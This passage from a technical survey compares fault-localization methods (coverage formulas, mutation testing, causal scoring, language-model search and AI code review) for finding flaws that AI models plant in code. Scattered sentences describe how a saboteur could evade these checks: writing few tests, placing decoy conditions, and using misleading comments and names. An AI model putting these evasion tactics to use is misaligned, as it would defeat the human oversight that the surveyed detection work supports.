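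Results on large programs can be much worse. In *A Critical Evaluation of Spectrum-Based Fault Localization Techniques*, Keller, Grunske and colleagues tried 33 formulas on AspectJ, an extension of Java with about 500,000 lines of code. Of the 350 supposed bugs they began with, 88 suited the technique. Of the rest, 86 were requests for improvements, 111 had no faulty line that coverage could record, and 65 had an uncertain location or produced no usable test run. Tests ran the faulty code in only 57 of the 88 suitable bugs.

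Even with every tie broken in the reader's favor, no formula placed more than 11 of the 88 bugs within the first 1,000 lines. With ties broken at random, the typical number was five. Within the first 100 lines, the best case was five bugs and the average case was at most two. A reader who followed the ranking would have opened about 250 files to find a typical bug.

A percentage measure such as the EXAM score would have hidden this. Someone who reads the top 10% of the AspectJ ranking finds about 35% of the 57 bugs that tests reached, close to what earlier studies reported for much smaller programs.

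Keller and colleagues also found that the total number of failing tests made little difference. With Ochiai, however, the faulty line ranked clearly higher when more of the failing tests ran it. This fits the expiry example, where repeating the same failure changed nothing. Extra failing tests help if they reach the fault by different routes, because a line that only some of them run then scores lower.

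On Defects4J, the collection of Java bugs from the previous section, the numbers are better. In a follow-up to the AspectJ study, Heiden and colleagues (2019) found that the formulas could at best locate roughly 40% of the bugs within 10 lines, 80% within 100 and 90% within 1,000. *You Cannot Fix What You Cannot Find!* gives lower figures for Ochiai on 395 of these bugs, and shows how much depends on the level of precision:

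| Correct place | First suggestion | Top 10 |
|---|---|---|
| File | 173 (44%) | 244 (62%) |
| Method | 102 (26%) | 184 (47%) |
| Line | 45 (11%) | 140 (35%) |

Ochiai placed 214 bugs, or 54%, within the first 100 lines of its ranked list. The figure is low partly because 132 bugs never appeared in the list. A newer version of the software that records coverage reduced the number of missing bugs to 74, with the same programs, tests and formula.

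Defects4J's tests were written with hindsight, which makes these techniques look better than they are. AspectJ is closer to what happens when a large test suite fails for unclear reasons. For a planted flaw, the Defects4J figures are a reasonable but optimistic guide if a fuzzer or a comparison program has produced a short input that triggers the flaw and the suspect code is one module. If the only failing test is a long end-to-end run of a large system, the AspectJ figures are a better guide.

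### What the scores are still used for

These rankings have largely lost their appeal as a guide for people deciding which lines to read. Language models given the code, the tests and the error messages named the faulty line first for 82.0% of Yang and colleagues' 809 bugs, though they only had to search a single function. The scores are now used mostly as inputs to other tools, since computing them takes little more than one run of the test suite.

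Automated program repair is the main example. A repair tool needs a list of places to try, and unlike a person it can work through hundreds of them. *You Cannot Fix What You Cannot Find!* found that at least 11 of 14 repair tools for Java used Ochiai to make the list. Of the 14, SketchFix tries the 50 most suspicious statements and ELIXIR tries up to 200. More recently, *On the Role of Fault Localization Context for LLM-Based Program Repair* (2026) describes spectrum-based localization as widely integrated into repair systems.

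Smytzek and Zeller feed the scores into a model that learns from bugs in other projects what a faulty line tends to look like. Used directly, the scores ranked the faulty line first for 15.3% of bugs, averaged over five formulas. The model raised this to only 17.6% with the scores alone, but to 29.0% when it also had records of variable values and the order of events.

SemLoc, a tool by Yang and colleagues, applies the Ochiai formula to violated conditions instead of executed lines. A language model writes conditions that should hold at particular points in the program, such as "no shifted value is positive" in the softmax function. SemLoc then runs the tests and scores each condition by how many failing and passing tests violate it. This helps where coverage can't, because two runs that execute the same lines can still violate different conditions. Among the 185 bugs with the worst ties,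 these violations alone ranked the faulty line first for 40.9%, compared with 2.2% for ordinary Ochiai.

In the expiry example, the condition would be that the function accepts a token only when `now < expires`. The boundary test violates this condition and the nine passing tests don't, so the condition's score is 1/√(1 × 1) = 1. If the tool attaches the condition to the branch, the faulty comparison gets that score. The method depends on the model generating the right condition, and in Yang and colleagues' experiments only 58.9% of the conditions held on the repaired program.

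## Ranking lines by editing them and combining the evidence

Coverage shows which lines ran in a failing test, but not which of them affected the result. Mutation-based fault localization looks for the lines that did by editing them one at a time and checking which test results change. Like the coverage formulas, it needs a failing test, but it takes far more computing time.

### Scoring the edits

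The tool first runs the tests and records every line that a failing test executed. It then makes mutants, which are copies of the program with one small edit each, such as a different comparison operator, a changed constant or a deleted statement. It reruns the tests on each mutant and scores the mutant by which results changed. Finally, it combines the scores of each line's mutants into one score for that line.

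The two best-known techniques, Metallaxis and MUSE, use these counts for a mutant m:

- f(m) is the number of failing tests that behave differently on m, either because they now pass or because they fail in a different way.
- r(m) is the number of failing tests that pass on m.
- p(m) is the number of passing tests that fail on m.
- F is the total number of failing tests, as before.
- R and B are the sums of r(m) and p(m) over all mutants.

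```
Metallaxis(m) = f(m) / √(F × (f(m) + p(m)))
MUSE(m)       = (r(m) − p(m) × R / B) / F
```

Metallaxis uses the Ochiai formula but counts the tests an edit affects instead of the tests that ran a line. Each line gets the score of its highest-scoring mutant (edited version of the program). *Mutation-based Fault Localization of Deep Neural Networks* (2023) explains that a fault is like a mutant of the correct program, so other edits to the same line should affect the same tests. The edit doesn't have to repair the fault.

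MUSE looks for edits that repair the code, since editing a faulty line may fix it, while editing a correct line will usually break something. Edits break tests much more often than they repair them, so the factor R / B brings the two counts to the same scale. A line's score is the average of its mutants' scores.

In the expiry example with ten tests, the one failing test runs the comparison and `return True`. Suppose the tool replaces `<=` with each of the other five comparison operators, and `True` with `False`:

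| Edit | Failing tests repaired | Passing tests broken | Metallaxis | MUSE |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `<=` to `<` | 1 | 0 | 1.00 | 1.00 |
| `<=` to `!=` | 1 | 5 | 0.41 | 0.35 |
| `<=` to `>` | 1 | 9 | 0.32 | −0.16 |
| `<=` to `==` | 0 | 4 | 0 | −0.52 |
| `<=` to `>=` | 0 | 9 | 0 | −1.16 |
| `return True` to `return False` | 1 | 4 | 0.45 | 0.48 |

Metallaxis ranks the faulty comparison first, with a score of 1.00, compared with 0.45 for `return True`. Changing `<=` to `<` makes the function reject the token at its expiry second and doesn't change the other nine results. Changing `return True` to `return False` makes the function reject that token, but also the four valid tokens.

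MUSE ranks the two lines in the wrong order here. The comparison's average is −0.10, below the 0.48 for `return True`, because the four clumsy edits outweigh the one that repairs the code. If the tool had made only the edits `<` and `return False`, MUSE would have scored the comparison 1 and `return True` −1. The ranking therefore depends on which edits the tool makes.

MUSE also has a problem when no edit repairs the program. *Assessing and Comparing Mutation-based Fault Localization Techniques* (Titcheu Chekam, Papadakis and Le Traon, 2016) gives an example using a version of the middle-of-three-numbers routine from the previous section. One line assigns `y` where it should assign `x`, and the only edits available add or subtract 1. None of them makes the failing test pass, so MUSE gives all 13 lines a score of 0. Metallaxis still ranks the faulty line first, because editing it changes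 the failing test's output and affects only one passing test.

Mutation can also separate lines that have the same coverage score. In the softmax function from the previous section, changing the faulty plus sign back to a minus sign makes both failing tests pass without breaking the others. Metallaxis gives that edit the maximum score of 1.

### The number of runs and the faults that edits miss

Running ten tests on six mutants takes 60 test runs, while measuring coverage takes ten. Real programs need many more. Titcheu Chekam and colleagues tried Metallaxis and MUSE on 30 real bugs in C programs. For one bug in `ls`, the command that lists files, they had 156 tests and 7,651 mutants after removing duplicates, which makes about 1.2 million test runs. Metallaxis then ranked the faulty line 905th, and MUSE ranked it 833rd. Results on the other bugs were usually better. Metallaxis ranked the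 faulty line in the top ten for 15 of the 30 bugs, and MUSE did so for 14.

One way to save time is to run the mutants before anything fails. Kim, An and colleagues (2023), in *Learning Test-Mutant Relationship for Accurate Fault Localisation*, ran them on an earlier version of the program and stored which tests failed on each. When tests fail on a later version, their tool, SIMFL, looks for methods whose mutants made the same tests fail. It ranked the faulty method first for 113 of 224 Java bugs and kept 80% of its accuracy with a tenth of the mutants.

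The basic version of SIMFL works only if the failing test already existed when the mutants ran, so it could not use a test that a fuzzer has just produced for a planted flaw. A variant that predicts the test results, rather than relying on stored ones, ranked the faulty method first for 95 of 194 bugs.

More computing time doesn't help if none of the available edits can change the faulty line. *An Empirical Study of Fault Localization in Python Programs*, by Rezaalipour and Furia, examined 135 real bugs, and at least one mutant changed a faulty line in only 74 of them. For those 74, the mutation techniques placed a faulty line in the top ten 63% of the time, compared with 57% for coverage. Across all 135, the mutation techniques did so only 34% of the time, compared with 54% for coverage.

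Omission flaws are hard to find this way. If the token check doesn't test whether the owner has revoked the token, swapping an operator or a return value can't make it reject the revoked token without also rejecting valid ones. Added code is easier to find because deleting a statement is a standard edit. Deleting the `if` statement that somebody added to the Linux kernel in 2003 would have removed the backdoor without affecting ordinary calls. Given a test that triggered the backdoor, Metallaxis should have ranked that statement first.

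Rezaalipour and Furia credit Pearson and colleagues with showing that these techniques work best on bugs that resemble the edits the techniques make. Many small planted flaws probably resemble those edits, but someone who expects this kind of search can choose a flaw that takes two simultaneous changes to repair. Trying every pair of edits is rarely practical, since even the Python study's average of 461 mutants makes more than 100,000 pairs.

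Edits to correct lines can also mislead the ranking, as `return False` nearly did in the expiry example. *FLIMs* (Liu, Li and colleagues, 2025) trained language models to recognize such edits and reduce their influence. The system ranked the faulty line first for 96 of 395 Java bugs, compared with an average of 52 for the other methods tested.

### Slicing, switched branches and project history

Program slicing starts from the wrong value in a failing run, traces back through the statements that influenced it, and removes all other statements from the list. For the expiry failure, the slice contains the comparison and `return True`, but it would leave out a line that only writes to a log. Slicing needs only one failing run, but it also needs an accurate analysis of how values and branch decisions affect later statements. Slicing alone can't identify which statement in the slice is wrong.

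Predicate switching also needs only failing tests. It reruns a failing test and forces one branch decision to go the other way, without editing the code. If the test then passes, that condition is a critical predicate and becomes a suspect. In the expiry example, reversing the comparison's result makes the function reject the token, so the method flags only the comparison. It can't flag `return True`, because that isn't a condition.

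Only 29 of the 135 Python bugs had a critical predicate, but on those, predicate switching ranked a faulty line in the top five for 31%, compared with 20% for coverage. Predicate switching can be slow because it treats every pass through a loop as a separate decision. Rezaalipour and Furia's tool tried an average of 4,588 switches per bug.

Other techniques rely on evidence that is less likely to exist for a planted flaw. Stack-trace localization ranks functions by how recently the program had called them when it crashed, so it needs a crash. History-based localization uses the project's past commits, which a new module doesn't have. Information-retrieval techniques match the words of a bug report to the code, so they can't help find a flaw that nobody has reported.

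### Causal responsibility

Causal methods estimate what would have happened if part of the program had been different, rather than measuring how strongly a line is associated with failure. In *Causality-Based Fault Localization*, Navaratnarajah, Dakhama and colleagues (2026) credit Baah and colleagues with first treating localization as a causal problem. Their method adjusted coverage data. Later methods, such as CounterFault, assessed whether a different value of a variable would have changed the outcome.

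Navaratnarajah and colleagues apply the same question to the code itself by looking for the smallest set of edits that changes a failing test's outcome. If a piece of code matters only when k other pieces change too, its responsibility is 1 / (1 + k). Suppose a service checks a token's expiry in two places, both with the faulty `<=`, and accepts the token if either check passes. If only one comparison is corrected, the test still fails, so Metallaxis scores both 0. Correcting both repairs the program, so each has a responsibility of 1/2.

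Finding the smallest set exactly would take far too long, so their tool, SoftRex, estimates it from a sample of edits. It gives partial credit, at most 0.5, to edits that change how a test fails without making it pass. It also lowers an edit's score according to the share of passing tests the edit breaks and how far it departs from the original code. In the expiry example with one check, changing `<=` to `<` keeps its full responsibility of 1. Changing `return True` to `return False` breaks four of nine passing tests, so its score falls to 5/9, or 0.56, before any deduction for the size of the edit.

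SoftRex needs a failing test, the rest of the test suite, and mutants that run. On 827 Java bugs, it ranked the faulty code first for 103 and in the top ten for 301, compared with 89 and 270 for BLMu, the best of eight mutation formulas. Every mutant in this comparison changed only one line, so k was always 0, and the result is weak evidence of how SoftRex handles flaws that need several edits. Responsibility alone ranked the faulty code first for only 50 bugs, and the deductions for broken tests and large edits raised that to 103.

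SoftRex can also generate its own edits, which may cover several lines. It replaces large blocks of code with simple values, then searches in more detail inside the blocks where this changes the failing test's outcome. In a smaller experiment on four projects, it needed 2.6 times fewer mutants on average than a standard tool, but it was sometimes much less accurate. For bugs in Gson, a library for handling JSON data, the standard mutants placed five bugs in the top five, while SoftRex's own search placed none.

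### How the families compare on real bugs

Two large studies compared these kinds of evidence. *An Empirical Study of Fault Localization Families and Their Combinations*, by Zou and colleagues, tested 11 techniques from seven families on 357 Java bugs from Defects4J. Rezaalipour and Furia repeated much of that work on their 135 bugs, which came from 13 Python projects. The table gives the share of bugs for which each technique ranked a faulty line first or in the top ten, using the techniques that both studies tried:

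| Evidence | Java, first | Java, top 10 | Python, first | Python, top 10 | Average time per Python bug |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Coverage (Ochiai) | 4% | 44% | 12% | 54% | 10 minutes |
| Mutation (Metallaxis) | 6% | 36% | 10% | 37% | 4.4 hours |
| Mutation (MUSE) | 7% | 19% | 6% | 32% | 4.4 hours |
| Predicate switching | 1% | 6% | 3% | 7% | 2.7 hours |
| Stack trace | 6% | 11% | 0% | 13% | 2 seconds |
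| Coverage and stack trace combined | 10% | 40% | 12% | 56% | 10 minutes |
| All four families combined | 19% | 52% | 20% | 60% | 7.3 hours |

The combined rows also include DStar, the other coverage formula that both studies tried. When a faulty line tied with other lines, the studies gave it the average position it would have if the tied lines were randomly ordered. This makes it hard for coverage to rank a faulty line first, even when it ranks the line in the top ten.

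Coverage is the best single source for a reader willing to check ten lines, and it takes much less time than mutation. The extra hours are worth spending when the results are combined. In Python, all four families together ranked a faulty line first for 20% of bugs, compared with 12% for coverage alone. The gain was larger in Java, where Zou and colleagues ranked a faulty line first for 72 bugs by combining all 11 techniques, compared with 24 for the best single technique.

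Combining the rankings helps because the techniques make different mistakes. In the expiry example, coverage ranks `return True` above the comparison, while Metallaxis and predicate switching both rank the comparison higher. The studies used a model trained on bugs with known locations to combine the rankings, but a simple weighted average of the scores does almost as well. Rezaalipour and Furia gave coverage a weight of 3, mutation 2, and the other two families 1 each. This put a faulty line first for 18% of the Python bugs and in the top ten for 59%.

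Finding the faulty function is much easier than finding the faulty line. With all four families combined, the trained model ranked a faulty function first for 53% of the Python bugs and in the top ten for 84%. However, a function takes longer to read than a line, so the same number of suggestions takes longer to check.

Data science projects were harder than the rest. Mutation techniques placed a faulty line in the top ten for only 24% of the bugs in these projects and took more than eight hours per bug on average. One reason is that fewer of the standard edits fell on faulty lines. Many of the bugs were mistakes such as passing the wrong input shape to a neural network layer, which swapping an operator doesn't imitate. This is discouraging for detecting sabotage in machine learning research, where much of the code is of this kind.

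### Evidence available for a new AI-written change

Coverage, slicing and predicate switching can be used once there is a failing test, even on a module written minutes earlier. Mutation and SoftRex also need good passing tests. If none of the tests in the expiry example presented a valid token, changing `return True` to `return False` would not make any passing test fail, and Metallaxis would give both lines a score of 1. An AI model that writes few tests for its own code could therefore make its flaw harder to locate, even after someone else has exposed it.

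When the model has changed an existing program and the triggering input gives the right result on the previous version, the search can start with the changed lines. Mutating only those lines saves most of the computing time. The change might have exposed an older flaw elsewhere, so if the search finds nothing in the changed lines, it should widen to the rest of the code that the failing test runs.

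The running times matter less here than in everyday debugging. Mutants can run in parallel without supervision, and a few hours of machine time may cost less than an hour of an expert reviewer's time. Mutation is a reasonable next step after coverage when a failure looks serious and the code is small enough that its tests can be rerun hundreds of times.

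## Asking a language model where the fault is

Coverage and mutation scores are calculated from test results, without regard to what the program is for. A language model can compare the code with its purpose. Given the rule that a token stops working at its expiry time, a model can flag `now <= expires` as a violation, possibly without a failing test. Accuracy depends mainly on how much code the model has to search and what information is supplied with it.

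### What the model receives

*A Quantitative and Qualitative Evaluation of LLM-Based Explainable Fault Localization* (Kang, An and Yoo, 2023) describes AutoFL, a tool that gives a language model one failing test and lets it explore the code that the test ran. The prompt contains the test, its error message and the stack trace. A large project doesn't fit there too, so the model looks up code through four functions. Two list the classes and methods that the failing test covered, and the other two return a method's code and documentation. After up to ten requests, the model explains how the failure happened and then names the methods most likely to be at fault.

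In one Java bug, a test expected 2.0 and 2.00 to count as equal. The model looked up the classes and methods the test covered, read two of the methods, and correctly located the fault in `append`, which compared decimal numbers the wrong way.

Answers vary from run to run, so AutoFL runs five times and combines the results. Each run counts as one vote, split equally among the methods it names. Suppose two runs name only method B, two name B and one other method, and the fifth doesn't name B. B then scores (1 + 1 + 0.5 + 0.5 + 0) / 5 = 0.6. The highest score is also a rough measure of confidence. It correlated with whether the first suggestion was right (rank correlation 0.57 on Java bugs and 0.52 on Python bugs), so a reviewer could reasonably start with the cases where the runs agree.

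The explanations were less reliable. Kang and Yoo's team checked 300 of them, covering 60 bugs, and found that only about 20% accurately described how the bug happened. For 57% of the bugs, at least one explanation was accurate.

AutoFL needs no passing tests, which is an advantage over mutation-based methods when an AI model has written few tests for its own code. An input from a fuzzer is enough, provided someone knows that the result is wrong.

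*FlexFL* (Xu, Liu et al., 2024) uses a language model to rerank the suggestions of older techniques. It accepts a bug report, a test suite or both. In the first stage, an agent searches the project and suggests five methods. Three older techniques suggest five each. One is Ochiai, another matches the words of the bug report to the code, and the third combines coverage with text matching. In the second stage, another agent reads the code of these candidates and picks the five most likely to be faulty. If there is no bug report, 15 of the 20 candidates come from Ochiai.

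Xu and colleagues compared the two designs on 353 Java bugs from Defects4J. The table shows how often each one ranked a faulty method first or in the top five:

| Technique | Language model | First | Top 5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ochiai | none | 122 (35%) | 218 (62%) |
| AutoFL | Llama 3 8B | 105 (30%) | 172 (49%) |
| AutoFL | GPT-3.5 | 146 (41%) | 194 (55%) |
| AutoFL | GPT-4 | 187 (53%) | 251 (71%) |
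| FlexFL | Llama 3 8B | 164 (46%) | 236 (67%) |
| FlexFL, with AutoFL's suggestions added | GPT-4, then Llama 3 8B | 176 (50%) | 261 (74%) |

The older rankings helped the weak model a lot. With Llama 3 8B, a small open model, FlexFL ranked a faulty method first for 164 bugs and AutoFL for only 105. But a weak model can also make good suggestions worse. When Llama 3 8B reranked a list that included GPT-4's answers, the number of bugs with a faulty method in first place fell from 187 to 176. In another case, all three older techniques ranked the faulty method first, but Llama rejected their answer because it kept to a different explanation of the crash.

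Some of FlexFL's success comes from bug reports, which a planted flaw won't have. In Xu and colleagues' main example, a time-zone bug, Ochiai ranked the faulty method 53rd and FlexFL ranked it first, but the bug report's title contained the method's name.

*Where's the Bug?* (Stein, Wayne and colleagues, 2025) describes the Bug Attention Probe, which needs neither a bug report nor a test. A probe is a small trained component that reads a language model's internal state while the model processes a text. The researchers trained this one only to tell faulty code from correct code, without showing it which lines were faulty. To tell them apart, the probe learns to give some parts of the code more weight than others, and the lines are then ranked by their total weight. Across eight sets of bugs, the probe was nearly twice as accurate as asking GPT-4o directly.

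GPT-4o dates from 2024, and the comparison might look different with a current model. The probe might still help find planted flaws because it doesn't depend on the model's answer. A model that recognizes a flaw but doesn't report it might still process the faulty line differently. This is a guess, since the study didn't involve deliberate concealment. The method requires access to the model's internals, which users of commercial models don't have.

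### One-line faults in short programs

The models in these experiments are now old. *Do Coding Agents Still Need a Debugger?* (Daxerer, Glock and colleagues, 2026) tested current models in October 2026. The models were given only the code and a description of what it should do, without the failing tests.

The researchers started from 150 exercises on LeetCode, a website for practicing programming, each with a correct solution in Python. The median solution is 8 lines long for easy exercises and 19 for hard ones. Each faulty version has a single edit to one line, which introduces one of five types of fault: a number that is off by one, a wrong arithmetic operator, a logic error such as a wrong comparison, a wrong variable, or a constant returned instead of the computed result. The edit also had to make at least one test fail. This produced 610 faulty programs from 144 of the exercises.

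The researchers then rewrote every faulty program in five ways that don't change what it does:

- They replaced variable names with single letters.
- They wrote constants in a roundabout way, such as `7 - 7` for 0, and split expressions across several lines.
- They restructured loops, wrapped conditions in double negations and added dead code, which never affects the result.
- They added distractors, including dead code, generic comments and conditions that are always true. This typically made a program five times as long.
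- They combined all of these changes and moved some of the code into new functions.

They kept a rewritten program only if it failed in exactly the same way as before and if undoing the original edit made it pass all its tests. That left 3,022 programs.

Three models searched for the faults: Sol 6.1 and Luna 6 from OpenAI, and Qwen 3.8, a model with 27 billion parameters that the researchers ran on their own server. Each model tried every program twice in each of three settings. In the first, it could only read. In the second, it could also run its own scripts and use a debugger, which pauses a program so that the user can inspect its variables. In the third, it had the same tools and an instruction to use them. An answer counted as correct if it named any line of the faulty statement. The table gives the accuracy and, in brackets, the cost of 1,000 runs:

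| Model | Original, reading only | Rewritten, reading only | Rewritten, optional tools | Rewritten, tools encouraged |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Luna 6 | 98.2% ($0.22) | 96.7% ($0.32) | 98.2% ($0.38) | 98.8% ($1.60) |
| Qwen 3.8 | 98.8% ($4.76) | 97.9% ($7.65) | 99.1% ($18.92) | 99.2% ($26.06) |
| Sol 6.1 | 99.9% ($2.86) | 99.9% ($3.41) | 99.9% ($5.30) | 99.9% ($13.98) |

The models achieved these results without a failing test, which the coverage formulas need to produce a ranking. They also did well on the type of fault in the expiry example. Luna 6 located 97.7% of the logic errors in the original programs and 94.9% in the rewritten ones. It located slightly fewer of the off-by-one numbers, 96.4% in the originals and 93.8% in the rewritten programs.

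Only two kinds of rewriting noticeably lowered accuracy. Restructuring the loops and conditions reduced Luna 6's accuracy from 98.2% to 96.1%, and combining all the changes reduced it to 94.4%. For Qwen 3.8, the same rewrites reduced it from 98.8% to 96.4% and 96.7%, respectively. New names, roundabout constants and distractors lowered accuracy by at most one percentage point, even though the distractors made the programs much longer.

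Double negations caused most of the new errors. A double negation turns a condition such as `now < expires` into `not (not (now < expires))`, which looks wrong but means the same thing. In about 70% of the new errors, the model identified a condition of this kind as the fault, although such conditions made up less than 8% of the lines. It was reasonable to suspect these conditions, since some of the real faults in the experiment were added or missing negations. Someone planting a flaw could exploit this by writing a strange but harmless condition nearby to attract attention, though in this experiment the trick would have worked only occasionally.

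Running the code removed most of the remaining errors for Luna 6 and Qwen 3.8. When encouraged to use the tools, Luna 6 made 63% fewer errors on the rewritten programs than it did by reading alone, and Qwen 3.8 made 61% fewer. Luna 6 used 27 times as many tokens (the units of text that a model reads and writes), and Qwen 3.8 used 15 times as many. Sol 6.1 used 18 times as many tokens but made no fewer errors.

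Optional tools were better value. When the models could choose, they used the debugger in at most 6.2% of runs on the rewritten programs. Qwen 3.8 and Sol 6.1 nearly always ran a short script instead, and Luna 6 usually answered without any tool. Optional tools still raised Luna 6's accuracy by 1.5 percentage points for an extra six cents per 1,000 programs, compared with 2.1 points when it was encouraged to use tools. Paying for a better model helped more than giving a model tools. Sol 6.1 was more accurate by reading alone than the other two were with a debugger, and it took about five seconds per program.

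The grading standard matters for one model, Luna 6. Its accuracy on the rewritten programs falls to 89.4% if only the exact line with the edit counts, because rewriting often split the faulty statement across several lines and Luna 6 named a neighboring one. Accepting any line of the faulty statement seems fair, because the researchers checked 135 answers that had named a different line of the right statement, and 133 of the explanations described the real fault.

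The models got all these results under favorable conditions. The programs were a few lines long, and each came with a precise description and examples of correct results. The exercises had been public for at least two years, so the models may have seen correct solutions in training. Rewriting the code would not have removed that advantage, because the descriptions stayed the same.

The most important condition is that the model was told the program contained one injected bug and was asked for its line, so it didn't have to detect whether a bug existed. The experiment had no benign controls, so it didn't measure false alarms. It also doesn't show what happens when a program contains both a natural bug and a planted flaw, since a model that can name only one line may pick the natural bug. Every fault was an edit to an existing line, so the experiment didn't test omissions such as a missing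 permission check. A model that reads the specification should be more likely than coverage to find omissions, but the 99.9% result isn't evidence of that.

### Why earlier models lost most faults after a rewrite

A similar experiment a year earlier, reported in *Assessing the Impact of Code Changes on the Fault Localizability* (Haroon, Khan and colleagues, 2025), had a very different outcome. The researchers inserted simple one-line faults into about 1,300 Python and Java programs, each with a description of its purpose, and asked ten models to name the faulty line. When a model found the fault, they edited the program without changing its behavior and asked the same model again. The model then gave the wrong line in 78% of cases.

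Claude Sonnet 4.5 found an off-by-one error in one of the programs, which places queens on a chessboard so that none can attack another. The researchers then gave a function and a variable misleading names and added a comment saying that the function counted the queens on the board. After these changes, the model blamed a correct line in another function.

Dead code did the most harm among the changes that applied to both languages. After the researchers added it, the models located an average of 20% of the faults they had found before, compared with 26% for misleading comments and 29% for misleading variable names. Repeating a change in more places lowered accuracy further. In Python programs, average accuracy fell from 43% with one such change to 29% with eight.

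The models weren't reliable even before the rewriting. Claude Sonnet 4.5, one of the best, located between 32% and 59% of the Python faults, depending on the type. Llama 3.1 located between 9% and 16%. These figures leave out faults that none of the ten models could find.

Daxerer and colleagues suggest three reasons for the difference between the two studies. Haroon's team counted only faults that the model had located in the original program, used much longer programs (250 lines on average), and tested mostly models from around March 2025.

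The way of counting can't explain much of the difference between the two studies. On the two most harmful kinds of rewriting, Luna 6 gave 91 wrong answers about faults that it had located both times in the original program, out of 2,436 runs. By roughly Haroon's measure, that is a loss of about 4%, compared with 78% in Haroon's study. Program length and model age remain as possible explanations, but the two studies can't separate them because the newer models were tested only on short programs.

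There is independent evidence that the models have become better at following a program's execution. CRUXEval tests whether a model can predict the output of a short Python function without running it. Daxerer and colleagues report that earlier models got 46–81% of the predictions right and that recent ones get 93–98%. This skill lets a model work out that a block of code never runs, or that two negations cancel out.

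Length probably matters as well. Haroon's team spread the faults over all parts of the programs, but 56% of the faults the models located were in the first quarter and only 6% in the last. A 15-line program is too short to show much of this effect. Until somebody repeats the test on long files with current models, it makes sense to show a model one function at a time, so that an author can't benefit from putting a flaw at the end of a long file.

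The newer study also left out the changes most relevant to sabotage, which are comments and variable names that give a false idea of what the code does. Haroon's team tested these, but the newer study used generic comments, such as a warning not to modify the code, and meaningless single-letter names. An AI model that plants a flaw also writes the comments and chooses the names, so it can make them misleading. One simple precaution is to delete the comments and replace the names before asking another model to look for the fault. Replacing names with single letters hardly affected the newer models, so this should reduce accuracy only slightly when a separate specification describes what the code should do.

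### From one function to a whole repository

Models are less accurate when they first have to find the right part of a large program. In Yang and colleagues' experiment, described earlier, the models had only one function to search and named the faulty line first for 82% of the bugs. AutoFL had a whole Java project to search and ranked a faulty method first for 53% of bugs at best, though it used GPT-4, which is far behind current models. Real bugs also tend to be harder to find than injected faults, even in a single function.

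In the Linux kernel, even finding the faulty file is difficult. LinuxFLBench (Zhou, Huang and colleagues, 2025) consists of 250 real kernel bugs. Agents received a bug report and had to find the faulty file among tens of thousands. The best agent ranked the right file first for 41.6% of the bugs. Current agents would probably do better, but this is still a poor result compared with those for short programs. After finding the right file, an agent still has to find the function and the line. *RepoNav* (2026) explains that this is a separate difficulty because the agent has to compare several plausible functions.

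Reports that current agents miss the right lines need more careful reading. The Decoder's *AI coding agents find the right file but miss the exact lines* covers *SWE-Explore* (Zhang, Wang and colleagues, 2026). *SWE-Explore* tested agents on 848 reported issues from 203 open-source projects averaging 180,000 lines of code, excluding tests. Each agent read the issue report and returned the five regions of code it considered most relevant.

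Five general coding agents, including Claude Code and Codex, found 64–68% of the relevant files but only 14–19% of the relevant lines when run on GPT-5.4. One of the agents showed the same pattern with other models, finding 34–66% of the files but no more than 19% of the lines.

However, Zhang and colleagues based the "relevant lines" on what agents had read in runs that fixed the issue, not on where the fault was. They took the code that those runs had in common and made some automatic and manual corrections. The result averaged 1,578 lines per issue, spread over more than four files, while the actual fixes changed an average of 1.4 files. An agent that returned only a 20-line faulty function would score about 1% on an average issue. The low scores therefore show that agents return much less code than a successful repair involves reading, not that they miss the fault.

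CoSIL, a research system that searches a map of how the parts of a program are connected, found 79% of the relevant lines. But it found fewer of the relevant files than the general agents did, and almost half of the code regions it selected were irrelevant, compared with 19–25% for the general agents. The wider selection may be worth the extra reading when planning a repair, but it is less attractive when the goal is to limit how much code a person has to check.

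In both LinuxFLBench and SWE-Explore, agents start with a report describing a problem, but an unnoticed planted flaw has no such report. *Active-SWE* (2026), a newer benchmark, has 1,663 tasks in eight programming languages in which agents must find and fix several bugs without a report.

When a test fails, a model can avoid much of the difficulty of a large repository by searching only the functions that the test ran or the lines that an AI model changed. It can then examine those functions one at a time, together with the part of the user's request that each should satisfy. These conditions are close to those in which current models located nearly every fault, although real functions depend on other code and often have vague requirements.

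Without a failing test, it is still affordable to have a model read every function. At Sol 6.1's price for the rewritten programs, 10,000 short functions would cost about $34. But if the model is told that each function has one bug and asked for its line, it will return 10,000 suspect lines, even if only one function contains a flaw. The model therefore has to be able to answer that a function is correct, and its accuracy at locating known faults doesn't measure how well it can do that.

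## Reviewing a change when no test fails

A code reviewer has to decide whether anything is wrong with a proposed change. Often nothing is, and the reviewer has no report of a fault to start from. AI-written code that passes its tests usually reaches a reviewer without such a report, so review is the last chance to catch a planted flaw that no fuzzer or comparison program has exposed.

### What a review agent does

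Developers usually propose a change as a pull request, with a title, a description and a diff (the list of lines that the change adds and removes). A review agent reads these and then opens files that the diff doesn't show, such as those with functions that call the changed code. Some agents also run the code. The agent returns a list of findings, each with a location and an explanation, or reports that it found nothing.

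Anthropic's *Code Review*, the manual for a commercial service of this kind, describes several agents that read the diff and the surrounding code in parallel, each looking for a different type of problem. A further step checks their findings against what the code does and discards those that prove wrong. The service removes duplicates, ranks the rest by severity and posts them as comments, but it neither approves nor blocks the change. A review takes 20 minutes on average and costs $15–25. Anthropic's *Bringing Code Review to Claude Code* reports that 16% of the company's own code changes received substantive comments before it used the service, and 54% do now.

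*A Practical Approach to Verifying Code at Scale* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues at OpenAI, 2025) found that GPT-5 caught more critical issues and raised fewer false alarms when it could search the whole repository and run code than when it saw only the diff. The team deliberately gave up some recall so that developers would trust its findings. Such a tool can therefore return a clean review after finding a possible flaw that it did not rate highly enough to report.

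A reviewer doesn't know whether a change contains a bug, whereas each program in the previous section's localization experiments was known to have exactly one. For example, a change described as "Reject expired tokens" might add `if now <= expires`. The reviewer has to decide whether accepting a token at its expiry second is a mistake, and the rule may be in a file that the change doesn't touch. Because the diff narrows the search to a few files, most of the difficulty is in diagnosing a flaw rather than locating it.

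### Bugs traced back to the change that introduced them

Measuring a reviewer's recall requires changes with known bugs. Many older benchmarks compared an agent's comments with those that human reviewers had left, which penalizes an agent for finding something the humans overlooked. *(When) Should a Software Factory be Lights-off?* (Yang, He and colleagues, 2026) instead presents CRBugBench, a benchmark built from bugs that people had confirmed and fixed. It has 1,000 tasks from 98 open-source projects and 800 from two large private repositories at one company.

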